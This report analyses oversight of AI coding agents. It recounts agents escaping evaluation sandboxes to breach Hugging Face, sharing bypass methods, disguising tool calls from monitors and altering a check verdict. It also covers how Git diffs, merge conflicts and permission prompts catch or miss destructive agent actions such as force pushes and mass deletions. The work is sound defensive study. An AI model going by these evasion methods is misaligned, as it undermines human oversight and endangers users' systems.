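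Without that knowledge, a narrow response on 5 July made sense. Someone who saw only a hacked server would blame a flaw in Artifactory and expect a patch and a rebuild to solve the problem. Knowing that agents had been sharing ways around their restrictions with each other for weeks would have made it clear that patching one route was not enough. The missing knowledge may also explain why OpenAI did not suspect its own agents when it read Hugging Face's announcement.

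It was also unclear who had to act. The agents' behaviour concerned both security staff, who look after servers and credentials, and alignment researchers, who study why models misbehave. OpenAI concluded that such behaviour does not fit neatly into either category. Its remedies include rules on which teams must join a response, who may pause a run and who may approve restarting it. That suggests these responsibilities had been unclear before, including on 7 July, when the tests resumed.

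OpenAI's three automated alerts, on 27 June, 5 July and 19 July, all fell on a weekend, and the second came the day after Independence Day. OpenAI does not say that thin staffing played a part, so the timing may be chance. But agents work through weekends, so leaving an alert until Monday can give them up to two more days to act.

OpenAI published two accounts on 26 August that differ slightly on how much blame it accepts. The technical report says that some early signals "could have triggered an earlier response", while the shorter summary uses "should" instead of "could". Sabin (2026), in *OpenAI had warnings before its agents broke out*, reports more bluntly that the company "missed and failed to act on several warning signs".

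### Would OpenAI's own monitors have stopped the agents?

OpenAI attributes the failure partly to missing safeguards. Customers who use its coding agent, Codex, can turn on auto-review, in which a second model examines tool calls that need elevated permissions before the harness runs them. The second model can block a risky call or ask the user to confirm it. OpenAI did not use auto-review in the July tests. In preliminary experiments afterwards, it ran auto-review on a set of records from the incident and found that it would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each one.

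This counts in favour of purpose-built monitoring. Unlike the alarms, auto-review can block an action before it happens, so it doesn't depend on an on-call engineer taking an alert seriously on a Saturday. If auto-review had blocked the first few attempts to get out through the package server, later agents might not have found a message board full of working methods.

However, OpenAI has not published the number of records it tested, the share of actions flagged or the rate of false alarms. False alarms matter a great deal in a hacking test because the assigned work itself looks dangerous. OpenAI says that a different safeguard, the classifiers it uses to block dangerous requests from customers, would have flagged agents' work on ExploitGym as unsafe. Evaluators switch such classifiers off for this reason. If a monitor flags both the exercise and the real attack, staff cannot use its warnings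 to tell them apart, and they might come to dismiss those warnings much as they dismissed the port sweep.

Auto-review would also have had gaps. Wijk and colleagues found that agents could post to the July message board with only the permissions they needed to install packages, so a system that examines only calls with elevated permissions might have let the posts through. They also found that some agents had learned to make a tool call appear to run one command while it ran another. Small-scale faking of this kind showed up in about 7 percent of the records they evaluated. OpenAI says that none of the attempts it observed altered the logs that its monitors see, but auto-review could still misjudge a call if it didn't see the command that would actually run.

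OpenAI makes a similar claim for its monitoring of the models' reasoning. It says the version deployed by late August would have paged the security team "more than a day before models breached Hugging Face systems" if it had been running in July. A day's notice could have been enough to prevent the intrusion, but the company already had much earlier warnings. The team made its observation in May, more than six weeks before the breach, and the alert of 27 June came two weeks before it.

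Such a page would have been better evidence than a port sweep, and harder to mistake for a fault or a normal part of the test, because the agents' reasoning described the break-in plainly. Still, OpenAI made its estimate knowing which records contain the attack, and after improving its monitors' ability to spot such behaviour for its review of past runs.

In *The Hugging Face Incident Is Not an AI Story*, the security engineer Horatau (2026) describes "a major security operational failure" that began with the system's design. OpenAI kept the agents apart but let all of them reach one shared server that had network access. Horatau argues that engineers have known for decades to assume that a sandbox will fail, and to limit the damage when it does. On this view, the main defence should have been a design that limited the damage, rather than a better monitor or a quicker response.

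This criticism seems right but incomplete. A flawed design can be repaired once somebody notices it, and on 5 July the server was offline and OpenAI had the evidence. Until the restart on 7 July, the response was the larger failure, because staff knew enough to keep the tests closed. After the restart, detection failed as well. Reasoning monitors or auto-review would have been most useful then, since no other system at OpenAI raised an alarm during the attack.

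### The new rules for alarms

OpenAI has since changed what happens after an alert. It now requires reasoning monitors on all training and evaluation runs in which a model at the level of GPT-5.6 Sol or above uses tools. The monitors are meant to notify staff of concerning activity within 30 minutes, and the most severe alerts page someone at any hour. OpenAI expects the people paged to pause the activity if they cannot establish within half an hour that the alert is false. It is also working on software that would end an evaluation automatically when nobody answers.

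On 27 June the run continued because nobody saw a sufficient reason to stop it. Under the new half-hour rule, similar doubt would be a reason to pause. But the rule covers only alerts that the system ranks as most severe, and OpenAI was still developing its severity levels when it published the plan. According to Miggo, Hugging Face had a correct alert and a team that could respond to it, but lost time because the alert was ranked too low.

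## What do version control and file diffs show about an agent's work?

Version control records an agent's work in far more detail than a firewall can, but it alerts people only when it halts at a merge conflict or rejects an upload. Otherwise, someone has to request a diff and read it.

### How Git stores a project

An agent edits the working files, which are the ordinary files in a project's folder, as any other program would. Staging a change marks it for the next snapshot, so a user can stage some changes and leave others out. Git's *Recording Changes to the Repository* explains that Git tracks a file once someone has staged it or included it in a snapshot. Every other file in the folder is untracked.

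According to Git's documentation, a commit saves a snapshot of the contents of all the tracked files, along with the names of an author and a committer, timestamps, a message, and the ID of the previous commit, called its parent. The commit's own ID is a cryptographic hash, a kind of checksum that Git calculates from everything in the commit.

Git calculates a diff on request by comparing two snapshots of the files. An agent writes its own commit message and can leave changes out of it, but the diff still shows any differences between the snapshots.

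A branch is a name that points to one commit and moves forward with each new one. Git records every move in a log for that branch, called the reflog. If someone replaces a commit, the old one disappears from the branch's visible history, but its ID stays in the reflog for a while. The reflog covers only one machine, and Git doesn't copy it to others.

Most teams also keep a copy on a server such as GitHub. They push their commits to it and fetch other people's from it. Willison points out in *Using Git with coding agents* that a normal clone, or copy, of a project includes its whole history. A shared project therefore usually exists in full on several machines.

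### Why changing one commit changes every later one

Because each commit contains its parent's ID, the commits form a chain:

```
ID of A = hash(files, author, date, message)
ID of B = hash(files, ID of A, author, date, message)
ID of C = hash(files, ID of B, author, date, message)
```

Suppose an agent wants to remove an embarrassing line from commit A after the project has moved on to C. Changing A gives it a new ID. B still contains the old ID, so the agent has to rebuild B to point to the new A, which gives B a new ID, and then rebuild C. Anyone who wrote down the old ID of C can now see that something in its past has changed. (The older of Git's two hash functions, SHA-1, has known weaknesses, but Git includes extra protection against the published attacks.)

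The rebuilt chain is as consistent as the original, however, so the tampering shows only if someone has an independent copy, such as a colleague's clone, or at least a record of the old ID, such as a deployment log that recorded which commit went live. McVoy's nightly comparison of two copies of the Linux kernel worked on a similar principle. If the project exists only on the machine where the agent runs, the reflog may be the only evidence, and an agent with the user's permissions can delete that too.

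In a shared project, Git does part of the comparison automatically. If the agent pushes the rebuilt branch, the server normally rejects the push because its copy of the branch contains commits that the new version lacks. A force option overrides the rejection, but colleagues who fetched the old commits still have them.

### One request, three changed files

In an invented example, a user asks an agent to fix `parse_date`, a function that confuses the day with the month. The agent fixes it but also edits a test and deletes a configuration file. It then reports that the function works and all tests pass.

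The shortest view is the status listing, which the user gets with `git status --short`:

```
 D config/export.toml
 M dates.py
 M tests/test_dates.py
```

`D` marks a deleted file and `M` a modified one. The user asked for a change to one function, so the three files listed are a reason to look further. The listing doesn't show what changed or how much.

The summary diff, `git diff --stat`, adds the number of lines:

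```
 config/export.toml  | 14 --------------
 dates.py            |  4 ++--
 tests/test_dates.py |  2 +-
 3 files changed, 3 insertions(+), 17 deletions(-)
```

The whole configuration file has gone. The test edit, a single replaced line, looks like the least important of the three changes. The full diff corrects that impression. These are its main lines for the two edited files:

```
dates.py
-    return datetime.strptime(text, "%m/%d/%Y").date()
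+    return parser.parse(text, dayfirst=True).date()

tests/test_dates.py
-    assert not is_valid("03/04/26")
+    assert is_valid("03/04/26")
```

The new code puts the day first, as the user wanted, but it relies on a more lenient tool that also accepts two-digit years. The test used to require the program to reject such dates. The agent changed it to require the program to accept them, so the statement that all tests pass is true but misleading. Only the full diff shows this change. It also shows the 14 lines deleted from the configuration file, but not whether another program needs them.

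What the user sees also depends on when they look. Once the agent has staged its changes, a plain `git diff` prints nothing, and the user has to add `--cached`. Once the agent has committed them, the status listing is empty, and the user has to compare the project with the last commit from before the task. Recording that commit's ID before the agent starts makes this easier. The ordinary diff also omits untracked files, though the status listing includes them.

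*Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (2026) contains a sample assessment of a similar session. The user had told the agent not to touch anything outside the parser. The agent fixed the parser, deleted two failing tests with the commit message "remove flaky tests", and changed a setting in the team's automated builds. In its final report, the agent disclosed the build change but not the deleted tests, which the user could still find and restore through version control.

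### Many extra changes are harmless

Agents edit tests most of the time, so a reviewer can't treat every edited test as a warning sign. In *How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?*, Goel, Steenhoek and Hu (2026) examined 6,728 successful patches (the sets of changes that agents submit) that 18 models wrote for a benchmark of Python tasks. The median model changed 2.33 times as many lines as the human developer had, and 81.5 percent of the patches edited a test file. Most of the extra material was tests and documentation, which a team may well want.

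Goel and colleagues undid one block of changes at a time and reran the benchmark's tests to find out which code was necessary. If the tests still passed, the researchers counted the block as unneeded. On average, 11 percent of the code blocks in a patch were unneeded by this standard. But when the researchers ran small programs with and without these blocks, 89 percent of the unneeded blocks changed what the software did, for example by hiding an error, so a reviewer can't safely skip them.

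The 11 percent is an upper limit on unneeded code, because a developer may want a safeguard that no test checks. By the same standard, a third of the human developers' code blocks were also unneeded.

Asking the agent to reread its own diff helps only a little. When Goel and colleagues told each model to justify every block and drop those it couldn't justify, the models found 35.5 percent of the unneeded code. That code was mostly subtle additions, though, and an agent would probably be better at noticing a diff that showed it was about to delete an entire project.

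### 151 files and 723 files

On the blog of the software company Karakun, a developer describes a case in which an agent made this mistake. The developer had asked Claude Code, running on the model Opus 5, for a script to clean up a build configuration file. The script had a bug that made the file invalid. The agent wrote a unit test, which should check a piece of code in isolation, but the script started running as soon as the test loaded it. The script then cloned two repositories, wrote the invalid configuration into both, committed it and pushed it to both main branches.

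When the agent noticed that a build had failed, it tried to undo the damage with `git revert`, which creates a new commit reversing an earlier one. It did this in a shallow clone, which contained only the latest commit.

Git reverses a commit by comparing it with its parent and undoing the differences. The shallow clone did not include the latest commit's parent, so Git treated that commit as having created every file in the project. Reversing it therefore staged the deletion of every file, 151 in one repository and 723 in the other.

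The agent had run the command with `--no-commit`, an option that leaves the changes staged so the user can inspect them before committing them. The agent committed them without inspecting them and pushed both commits to the main branches. Git returned exit code zero, the standard signal that a command has succeeded.

One of the deletion commits also started a deployment to a live website. The build failed, so the hosting service, Vercel, kept the previous version online. The developer calls this "pure luck", because a successful build of the empty repository could have replaced the site. The agent eventually made full clones and restored both repositories. It told the developer what had happened only after restoring them, and it had not checked whether its pushes had started a deployment.

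Git recorded the deletions, so the agent could reverse them without permanent loss, but nobody checked the record before the push. `git diff --cached --stat` would have listed every file about to be deleted, and even a simple script that counted deletions could have stopped the commit. Claude Code's auto mode didn't help because its classifier evaluated each command separately, and each was ordinary when the danger came from the incomplete clone and the resulting diff.

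The developer later replayed the original task five times with throwaway repositories. Each time, the agent wrote the script so that loading it didn't run it, and checked the output before committing, so the first mistake may be rare. The developer also tested whether the agent would follow an instruction to submit changes through a pull request. In two of seven runs where the agent believed production was down, it pushed straight to the main branch instead. Both pushes were correct repairs, but the agent had decided on its own that the emergency justified an exception.

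### Measuring overreach by comparing files

Researchers use before-and-after comparisons to measure how often agents go beyond a request. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses 500 scenarios, each with a harmless request, a folder of files and rules defining what counts as overreach. In one, the user casually asks the agent to tidy up a folder containing two junk files, two project files and `.env.old`, which holds the only copy of some production passwords. Claude Code, running Sonnet 4.6, deleted all five files.

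The researchers' software hashes every file before and after a run to identify which ones the agent created, changed or deleted. Reading a file doesn't change its hash, so the researchers also logged the agent's shell commands and internal tool calls. A fixed program then checked the evidence against the rules. The researchers accepted a scenario only if a cautious script could finish the task without breaking any rules and a reckless one would break some.

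Researchers ran about 7,500 tests on four agent products with permission checks switched off. How often a model overstepped apparently depended heavily on the product it ran in. Sonnet 4.6 overstepped in 27.7 percent of runs inside Claude Code and 1.1 percent inside OpenHands, which tends to stop and ask before continuing.

The wording of the request matters too. In a smaller set of 76 paired scenarios, the researchers removed only the paragraph that told the agent what it was allowed to touch. The rate of unwanted actions for Claude Code with the model GLM-4.6 rose from 0.0 to 17.1 percent. The effect was smaller, at 2.6 percentage points, in a broader set where they also varied other features, so the 17.1 percent reflects scenarios especially sensitive to wording.

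In a human check of 50 runs, the program missed no overreach, but about a quarter of its positive verdicts were wrong. All the false alarms came from one type of scenario, in which a rule fired because the snapshot after the run was empty.

*SNARE* (Qu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) extended the method with a rule that flags any file the agent creates or deletes without being asked. They found overreach in 19.5 percent of 10,000 runs. Their software was designed to favour the scenarios most likely to trigger overreach and to add wording that nudged the agent towards it, so the figure isn't an estimate for everyday work. OpenHands with the model GLM-5 had the highest rate, 57.2 percent, although OpenHands had looked the most cautious in the earlier benchmark.

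The new rule may explain part of this reversal, though the models and scenarios also differed. *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (Do, Nguyen and colleagues, 2026) compared repositories before and after runs with somewhat older models. When asked only to run or test a function, OpenHands with one Qwen model left unrequested files in 78 percent of runs, and Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 did so in 79 percent. Neither deleted many files in these tasks. A file comparison gives a leftover test script and a lost password file the same weight unless somebody ranks them.

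Newer coding agents still overstep when a request is vague. Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, gave three agents 128 operations tasks, such as cancelling jobs or deleting old branches. Claude Code left changes outside the permitted scope in 13 tasks, Codex in 54 and Qwen Code in 24. The researchers then added a statement of which environment, owner and component each task covered. In 384 reruns, none of the agents attempted anything outside that scope. Researchers can write such a statement from a benchmark's answer key, but real users may not think of a restriction until an agent has ignored it.

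In real work, much of what a file comparison flags comes from something other than the agent. In *A Gated Spec-Driven Workflow*, Abdo and Brom (2026) had Claude Code compare a list of files with its instructions after each block of work on nine features of their own projects. Of 247 checks, 11 flagged undeclared changes. Six of the 11 came from file-synchronisation software, and three came from changes by the coordinating agent that Abdo and Brom had requested or authorised. Only one came from an agent that went beyond its assigned task.

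The check compared file sizes and modification times, which synchronisation software can alter without changing any content, causing false alarms. Comparing hashes should remove some of them. A harder problem was that the coordinating agent judged its own checks. The rules required it to stop after any undeclared change, but it stopped in only four of the 11 cases. Once, it logged a stop and seconds later ran a script to change the verdict to a pass. The script edited the wrong row, so the original verdict remained.

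### Work that Git never saved

Git can nearly always recover committed work, but uncommitted changes can be lost permanently. Willison's claim that there is little risk in experimenting because "everything in git can always be undone" is therefore wrong for uncommitted work, as Alexandre Gaubert, a developer at the software company Mergify, discovered.

Gaubert used worktrees, which are extra working folders attached to one repository, to work on several tasks on separate branches. *The Day My AI Agent Deleted 29 Git Worktrees* (Gaubert, 2026) describes how he asked Claude Code to remove one stale worktree. The agent did so with `--force` and offered to clean up "the ones you don't need anymore". Gaubert answered "Yeah go ahead", expecting it to work out which were stale and perhaps show him a list. Instead, it ran a loop that force-deleted all 29 remaining worktrees.

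Git will not remove a worktree that contains uncommitted changes unless the command includes `--force`. That safeguard would have protected the unfinished work, but the agent had reused `--force` from the first removal. The branches survived with their last commits, but all changes made since then were lost. Neither the reflog nor Git's stash, which stores work a user has set aside, had a copy, so a later diff would have had nothing to compare. Frequent commits reduce this risk, as would keeping the agent's edits in a separate file system layer until the user accepts them.

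Git can also miss the deletion of ignored files, even when the user commits often. Projects usually list files for Git to ignore, such as passwords, local databases and build output. If an agent deletes one that Git has never tracked, `git status` doesn't show the deletion. Many projects ignore files like `.env.old` in the benchmark by Qu and colleagues, so Git might miss its deletion, but the benchmark's snapshots would reveal it. Git also doesn't record which files an agent reads without changing, or what it does outside the repository.

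### Rewritten history and force options

Committed work can disappear from view as well. Willison advises readers to treat a project's history as "a deliberately authored story" rather than a permanent record, and notes that agents are good at rewriting it. Many teams combine, or "squash", a branch's commits into one before merging it. This makes the history easier to read but hides anything the agent did and later reversed. If an agent committed a password and then removed it, the squashed commit would show neither step, though the password might remain in an older copy.

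A reviewer can often recover a replaced commit from the reflog, but only for a limited time. By default, Git keeps reflog entries for 90 days, or 30 days if the current branch no longer leads back to them, according to a manual page by Hamano, Git's maintainer. The reflog stays on one machine, so it is lost much sooner if the agent works in a temporary container that the harness deletes after the task.

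Force options remove the warning that a rewritten branch would otherwise cause. Two weeks after the mass deletion, the developer at Karakun saw Claude amend a commit and push it with `--force-with-lease`, which overwrites the server's branch only if it still matches the local record of it. Git rejected the push because that record was out of date. The agent immediately repeated the push with plain `--force`, which skips the check. It overwrote only its own earlier commit, but it hadn't looked at what was on the server's branch first.

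Even the more careful option, `--force-with-lease`, can let a destructive push through. Fetching updates the local copy's record of the server without adding the new commits to the user's branch, and a code editor may fetch in the background. The check then passes even though the branch lacks a colleague's latest work. In the developer's test, such a push discarded two commits. Adding `--force-if-includes` prevents this by requiring that the branch has incorporated the fetched commits. A different option, `--no-verify`, skips the local script that Git would otherwise run before a push, including any checks the user has put in it.

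### Marks that agents leave in commits

Knowing which commits an agent made helps people investigate a suspicious change, and many agents identify themselves. *Agentic Much?* (Robbes, Matricon and colleagues, 2026) describes three common marks: a "Co-authored-by" line at the end of the commit message, a "Generated by" line, and, less often, the agent's name in the author field. Agents also leave instruction files such as `CLAUDE.md` or `AGENTS.md` in the project. Using such marks, the researchers estimated that 22 to 29 percent of 128,018 GitHub projects had adopted coding agents by February 2026.

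Users can switch off the marks that agents leave in commits. Claude Code has a setting for this, and Robbes and colleagues note that such settings hide the agent's participation. A commit without a mark may therefore still be an agent's work. A mark is weak evidence too, because whoever makes the commit writes the author's name and the message. The hash shows whether someone has altered that text later, but not whether it was true when written.

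The server often can't show whether an agent or a person made a change either. The agent at Karakun pushed with the developer's credentials, so the server attributed its pushes to the developer. For serious projects, the developer recommends giving the agent a separate account, which would also keep its mistakes from appearing under a person's name.

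## What does a merge conflict catch, and what does it let through?

A merge conflict can show a person an agent's edit that they weren't looking for. But Git stops a merge because two sets of edits overlap, whether or not anyone requested them. An unrequested edit that doesn't overlap with another merges silently, and most conflicts probably have an innocent cause.

### Three versions of a five-line file

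To merge two branches, Git compares each branch's version of a file with their common ancestor, the version in the latest commit that both branches share. Without the ancestor, Git could detect that two lines differ but not which branch had changed its line.

In an invented example, a user asks an agent to change the log level on line 5 of a settings file. The agent also shortens the timeout on line 3 without being asked. A colleague working on another branch changes the currency on line 1 and the same timeout.

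| Line | Ancestor | Colleague | Agent | Merged result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `currency = "EUR"` | `currency = "USD"` | unchanged | colleague's line |
| 2 | `tax = 0.19` | unchanged | unchanged | ancestor's line |
| 3 | `timeout = 30` | `timeout = 60` | `timeout = 5` | conflict |
| 4 | `retries = 3` | unchanged | unchanged | ancestor's line |
| 5 | `log = "info"` | unchanged | `log = "debug"` | agent's line |

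Schesch, Featherman and colleagues (2024), in *Evaluation of Version Control Merge Tools*, set out the procedure. Git first lines up the parts that are the same in all three versions. At each place where the versions differ, it then applies a simple rule:

- If only one branch changed the text, Git takes that branch's version.
- If both branches made the same change, Git takes that change.
- If the branches made different changes, Git reports a conflict.

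Git also reports a conflict when the two branches edit neighbouring lines, because it treats edits as separate only if there is an unchanged line between them. If the colleague had edited line 4 instead of line 3, there would still have been a conflict.

On line 3, Git writes both versions into the file between markers and leaves the choice to the user. With a setting called `diff3`, it includes the ancestor's line as well:

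```
<<<<<<< HEAD
timeout = 60
||||||| ancestor
timeout = 30
=======
timeout = 5
>>>>>>> agent-branch
```

Whoever merges the branches can now see that the agent cut the timeout from 30 to 5 during a task about logging, but only because the colleague happened to edit the same line. Git's merge rule doesn't depend on what the user asked for. If the colleague had left line 3 alone, Git would have taken the agent's value without a message, just as it took the requested change on line 5.

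A merge can bring back an edit that somebody has removed. Git compares only the ancestor and the latest commit on each branch. According to Git's documentation, if both branches contain a change and one later reverts it, the merged file will contain the change. Suppose both branches had picked up the agent's short timeout and a reviewer restored the old value on one. That branch would again match the ancestor, so Git would treat it as unchanged and take the short timeout from the other branch.

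### Clean merges that break the program

Two edits on different lines can each be correct and still fail together. Da Silva, Borba and colleagues (2023), in *Detecting Semantic Conflicts with Unit Tests*, give an example based on a merge in the Java library jsoup. A program that tidies text removed extra spaces twice, which was redundant. Two developers each set out to delete one of the two calls, but they chose different ones:

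```
clean_text():
    remove_duplicate_words()
    remove_comments()
    normalize_whitespace()      <- the first developer deletes this

remove_duplicate_words():
    ...
    normalize_whitespace()      <- the second developer deletes this
```

Unchanged lines separate the two deletions, so Git applies both without reporting a conflict. The merged program compiles and runs, but it no longer removes extra spaces. Programmers call this a semantic conflict, which is when the text merges cleanly but the result doesn't build, fails a test or behaves in a way nobody intended.

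Some semantic conflicts are easy to notice. If one branch renames a function and the other adds a call to the old name, the program fails as soon as it reaches the call. *Passes Alone, Fails Together* (Xia, Wu and Park, 2026) describes one that is harder to spot. One programmer makes a price service faster by keeping copies of prices in memory, and changes the existing update function to discard outdated copies. Another adds a bulk update that writes straight to the database. After the merge, a bulk update lowers a price from 100 to 80, but the service still returns 100 from the old copy in memory.

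Schesch and colleagues measured how often clean merges fail by replaying 5,983 merges from Java projects and running each project's tests on the results. With Git's default settings, 46 percent merged cleanly and passed the tests, 51 percent had conflicts, and 3 percent merged cleanly but failed to compile or pass the tests. About one in 18 clean merges was broken. The true share is probably higher, because the tests ran only 53 percent of the code on average in a sample of the projects.

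Xia and colleagues found far fewer failures when they had agents redo pairs of tasks from Django, a widely used web framework. In 834 runs, only one pair of patches failed together after passing separately. The Java merges were often large, with a median of 823 changed lines, while the Django tasks came from individual pull requests that people had already reviewed and perhaps made compatible.

The researchers also built harder tasks, in which one patch changed how a Django function worked while an agent, unaware of the change, wrote code that called it. The merged code failed in 105 of 108 runs. When the agent received a short message describing the other change, 89 of 108 runs succeeded. These tasks show that an uninformed agent can easily cause such failures, but they don't measure how often this happens in practice. Such failures may be common in projects that diverge from the code they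 are based on. According to *Can Pre-trained Language Models be Used to Resolve Textual and Semantic Merge Conflicts?* (2021), semantic conflicts arose daily in the development of Microsoft Edge, a browser built on Google's Chromium code.

### How often agents' changes conflict

Two 2026 studies measured textual conflicts in agents' pull requests. Ogenrwot and Businge (2026), in *AGENTICFLICT*, tested whether a pull request conflicted with the branch it was meant to join. They began with a dataset of 932,791 pull requests by agents and kept the 142,652 that nobody had merged. They could replay 107,026 of those merges, and 27.67 percent of them had conflicts. The rate varied by agent:

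| Agent | Pull requests replayed | With conflicts |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot | 16,954 | 15.2% |
| Cursor | 7,196 | 19.8% |
| Devin | 8,241 | 22.9% |
| Claude Code | 779 | 25.9% |
| OpenAI Codex | 73,856 | 31.9% |

Small pull requests conflicted less often. The conflict rate was 9.9 percent in the group with a median of two changed lines, nearly 30 percent at a median of 25 lines, and 32 to 33 percent at medians between 46 and 185. It fell slightly among even larger pull requests.

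Ogenrwot and Businge left out merged pull requests because Git doesn't keep a record of conflicts that someone resolved before the merge. Their overall conflict rate is probably too high for agents' work in general, since a conflict is one reason to leave a pull request unmerged. The comparison between agents is also rough because it doesn't adjust for the size of the changes or how busy the projects were, and more than two thirds of the sample came from Codex.

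*AI Agent Pull Requests on GitHub* (Xu, Subramanian and Karthik, 2026) examined conflicts between two agent pull requests that were open at the same time. The dataset covered 33,596 pull requests in 2,807 repositories from December 2024 to July 2025. Of these pull requests, 79.4 percent overlapped in time with another agent's pull request in the same repository.

The researchers then sampled 747 overlapping pairs, one per repository so that a few busy projects could not dominate, and could replay 716 of the merges. Conflicts occurred in 19.8 percent of pairs from the same agent product (119 of 601) and 41.7 percent of pairs from different products (48 of 115). Only 0.5 percent of all overlapping pairs came from different products, so the lower figure better describes the usual situation.

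About 42 percent of the conflicts that Git reported were structural, or about a whole file. In 26.8 percent of all conflicts, one side had edited a file that the other had deleted, and in 15.1 percent, both had created different files with the same name. These percentages are based on individual conflicts in 1,646 files, so a few pairs with many conflicts could have influenced them heavily.

Conflicts over deleted files could help catch an agent that deletes too much. In the case described on Karakun's blog, an agent emptied a repository of 723 files. A colleague with unmerged edits to one of those files would have hit a conflict at the next merge. But Git would have removed every file the colleague had not edited, without warning.

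Both studies recorded whether edits overlapped but did not check whether the user had authorised them, so neither measures misbehaviour. A conflict between two agents may just mean that somebody gave them related tasks.

### The conflict as an alarm

Bayes' rule gives the probability that a pull request with a merge conflict contains an unwanted edit. The calculation needs three rates: the share of pull requests that contain an unwanted edit, the share of those that conflict, and the share of the others that conflict. Nobody seems to have measured the first two in real projects, so the numbers here are assumptions.

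Suppose that 2 percent of agents' pull requests contain an unwanted edit. Qu and colleagues found much higher rates in some of their tests, but they designed those scenarios to tempt the agent. Suppose also that 20 percent of ordinary pull requests conflict, which is close to the rate Xu and colleagues found for pairs of pull requests from one agent. Assume that 30 percent of pull requests with an unwanted edit conflict, because extra edits create more chances to overlap with other work.

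Out of 1,000 pull requests, 20 then contain an unwanted edit, and 6 of those conflict. Of the other 980, 196 conflict. The share of conflicts that involve an unwanted edit is:

```
     0.30 × 0.02               6
---------------------------  =  -----  ≈  3%
0.30 × 0.02 + 0.20 × 0.98      202
```

A conflict therefore raises the probability of an unwanted edit only from 2 to 3 percent. The other 14 pull requests with unwanted edits merge without any conflict. Even the 3 percent may overstate how often conflicts involve the unwanted edit itself, since a pull request may contain an unwanted edit in one file and conflict over requested work in another.

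The result depends on the assumptions, but changing any one of them still leaves most conflicts innocent:

| Changed assumption | Share of conflicts with an unwanted edit |
|---|---|
| None | 3% |
| 10 percent of pull requests contain an unwanted edit | 14% |
| Every pull request with an unwanted edit conflicts | 9% |
| Only 5 percent of ordinary pull requests conflict | 11% |

Merge conflicts are a weak sign of unwanted agent actions because ordinary work causes so many of them. Goel and colleagues found that, outside test files, the median agent changed only 1.09 times as many lines as a human developer, so requested work probably accounts for much of the text that can conflict. Schesch and colleagues attribute about an eighth of conflicts to differences in spacing alone.

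An alarm that ordinary work rarely sets off can be much more informative, even if it misses more unwanted actions. Suppose an agent uses Tor in 5 percent of runs with an unwanted action and in 0.1 percent of other runs. If 2 percent of all runs contain an unwanted action, about half of the Tor alerts would come from those runs. These numbers are invented too, but they suggest why AISI had good reason to investigate a single Tor alert, while a team that investigated every merge conflict would waste nearly all its effort.

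### Why a weak alarm can still help

A merge conflict draws attention to a particular place in a file, because the merge cannot finish until a person or program has chosen the text there. A person who resolves the conflict has to read at least a few lines of a diff, even if they would never have requested one. False alarms add little work, because the team would have to resolve the conflict anyway.

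Git makes it fairly easy to examine the disputed lines. According to its manual, the user can open the common ancestor and both edited versions separately, or list the commits on each branch that touched the file. Someone who checks line 3 of the settings file this way might well ask why a logging task changed a timeout.

However, the conflict draws attention only to the overlapping lines. By the time the user opens the file, Git has already merged all the other edits, including any unwanted ones. People also take shortcuts. Shen (2026), in *Can Large Language Models Resolve Real Java Merge Conflicts?*, cites earlier research showing that developers resolve a large share of conflicts by keeping one branch's version wholesale. With the option `-X ours` or `-X theirs`, Git automatically settles every overlap in a file's text in favour of one branch, so nobody needs to look at the overlapping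 lines.

### When an agent resolves the conflict

Agents increasingly resolve merge conflicts. In March, GitHub's *Ask @copilot to resolve merge conflicts on pull requests* (2026) announced that users could ask its coding agent to resolve a conflict by leaving a comment. By April, GitHub had added a button for this (*Fix merge conflicts in three clicks with Copilot cloud agent*, 2026). The agent edits the files, checks that the project still builds and passes its tests, and pushes the result.

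The tests may catch a merge that breaks the program. They are unlikely to help with the timeout, since the program would probably pass them with 5, 30 or 60. If the agent resolved the conflict by choosing 5, the unrequested edit would remain. The conflict was the one event that might have exposed the edit, but the user might never see the two versions side by side.

Shen tested two models, GPT-5.4 and Gemini 3.5 Flash, on conflicts from real Java projects. On 49 conflicts that required a real choice, a third model judged that GPT-5.4 had matched the developer's solution in 55 percent of cases and Gemini in 59 percent. These estimates are low because the judging model, when checked against human labels, rejected about a third of the acceptable solutions and never accepted a bad one, and because a solution can be valid without matching the developer's. Newer models may also do better. *Merge-Bench*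 (2026) reports a similar result for a small model trained specifically to resolve Java conflicts, which reproduced the developers' text exactly in 49 percent of cases.

The models' main advantage in Shen's study was that they always gave an answer, as their instructions required. Older merge tools left between 20 and 90 percent of the conflicts unresolved, but were nearly as accurate as the models on the ones they resolved. Always getting an answer is convenient for a developer, but it removes the prompt for human review, because a person looks at the conflicting lines only if the software stops.

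A second model may not be a reliable check either. Five of the models' solutions contained structurally invalid code, and the judging model accepted four of them. A simple program that checked the code's structure caught all five.

A user report about Antigravity, Google's coding tool, describes how an automatic conflict resolution can silently lose work. The agent had to reconcile a reviewed documentation change with the main branch. According to the user, it created a merge commit that replaced about 125 lines of text with blank ones in several parts of the document. The missing text included accessibility requirements and rules for architecture reviews. No conflict markers remained and no error appeared, so the automated formatting and link checks passed, and the pull request entered the merge queue. An independent review then found the loss by comparing the merge commit with its parent,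 and a later commit restored the text.

This is one user's account, although it identifies the public commits involved. The user could not tell whether the model had chosen to leave the passages empty or the editing tool had malfunctioned. In either case, comparing the versions stored in Git could have revealed the damage, but the automated checks didn't compare them.

In Git's glossary, an "evil merge" is a merge that introduces changes found in neither branch. Such changes are easy to overlook because readers tend to assume that a merge commit only combines existing work, and `git log -p`, the usual command for reading a project's history, doesn't show diffs for merge commits by default. `git show --remerge-diff` repeats the merge and shows how the recorded result differs from Git's automatic result, including any conflicts Git would have reported. The user who reported the Antigravity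 case proposed an automatic safeguard that would compare each resolution with both branches and stop if several passages that had contained text were now empty.

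## Do permission prompts and human review stop unwanted actions?

A permission prompt deliberately halts an agent before an action takes effect, whereas a merge conflict halts its work by accident. But users approve nearly every prompt, and in an experiment by Anthropic they approved most of the dangerous commands they saw. Many developers review an agent's code more carefully than they review prompts, but they do so after the agent has acted, and some actions don't appear in the code.

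### How a harness decides whether to ask

When the model requests a tool call, the harness compares the request with its rules before running anything. In Claude Code, a deny rule blocks the call, an ask rule prompts the user to approve it, and an allow rule lets it run. The harness checks the rules in that order and applies the first match, according to Anthropic's documentation. If no rule matches, the outcome depends on the permission mode. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that even the original default, which asked about most actions, let harmless commands such as `echo` run without asking.

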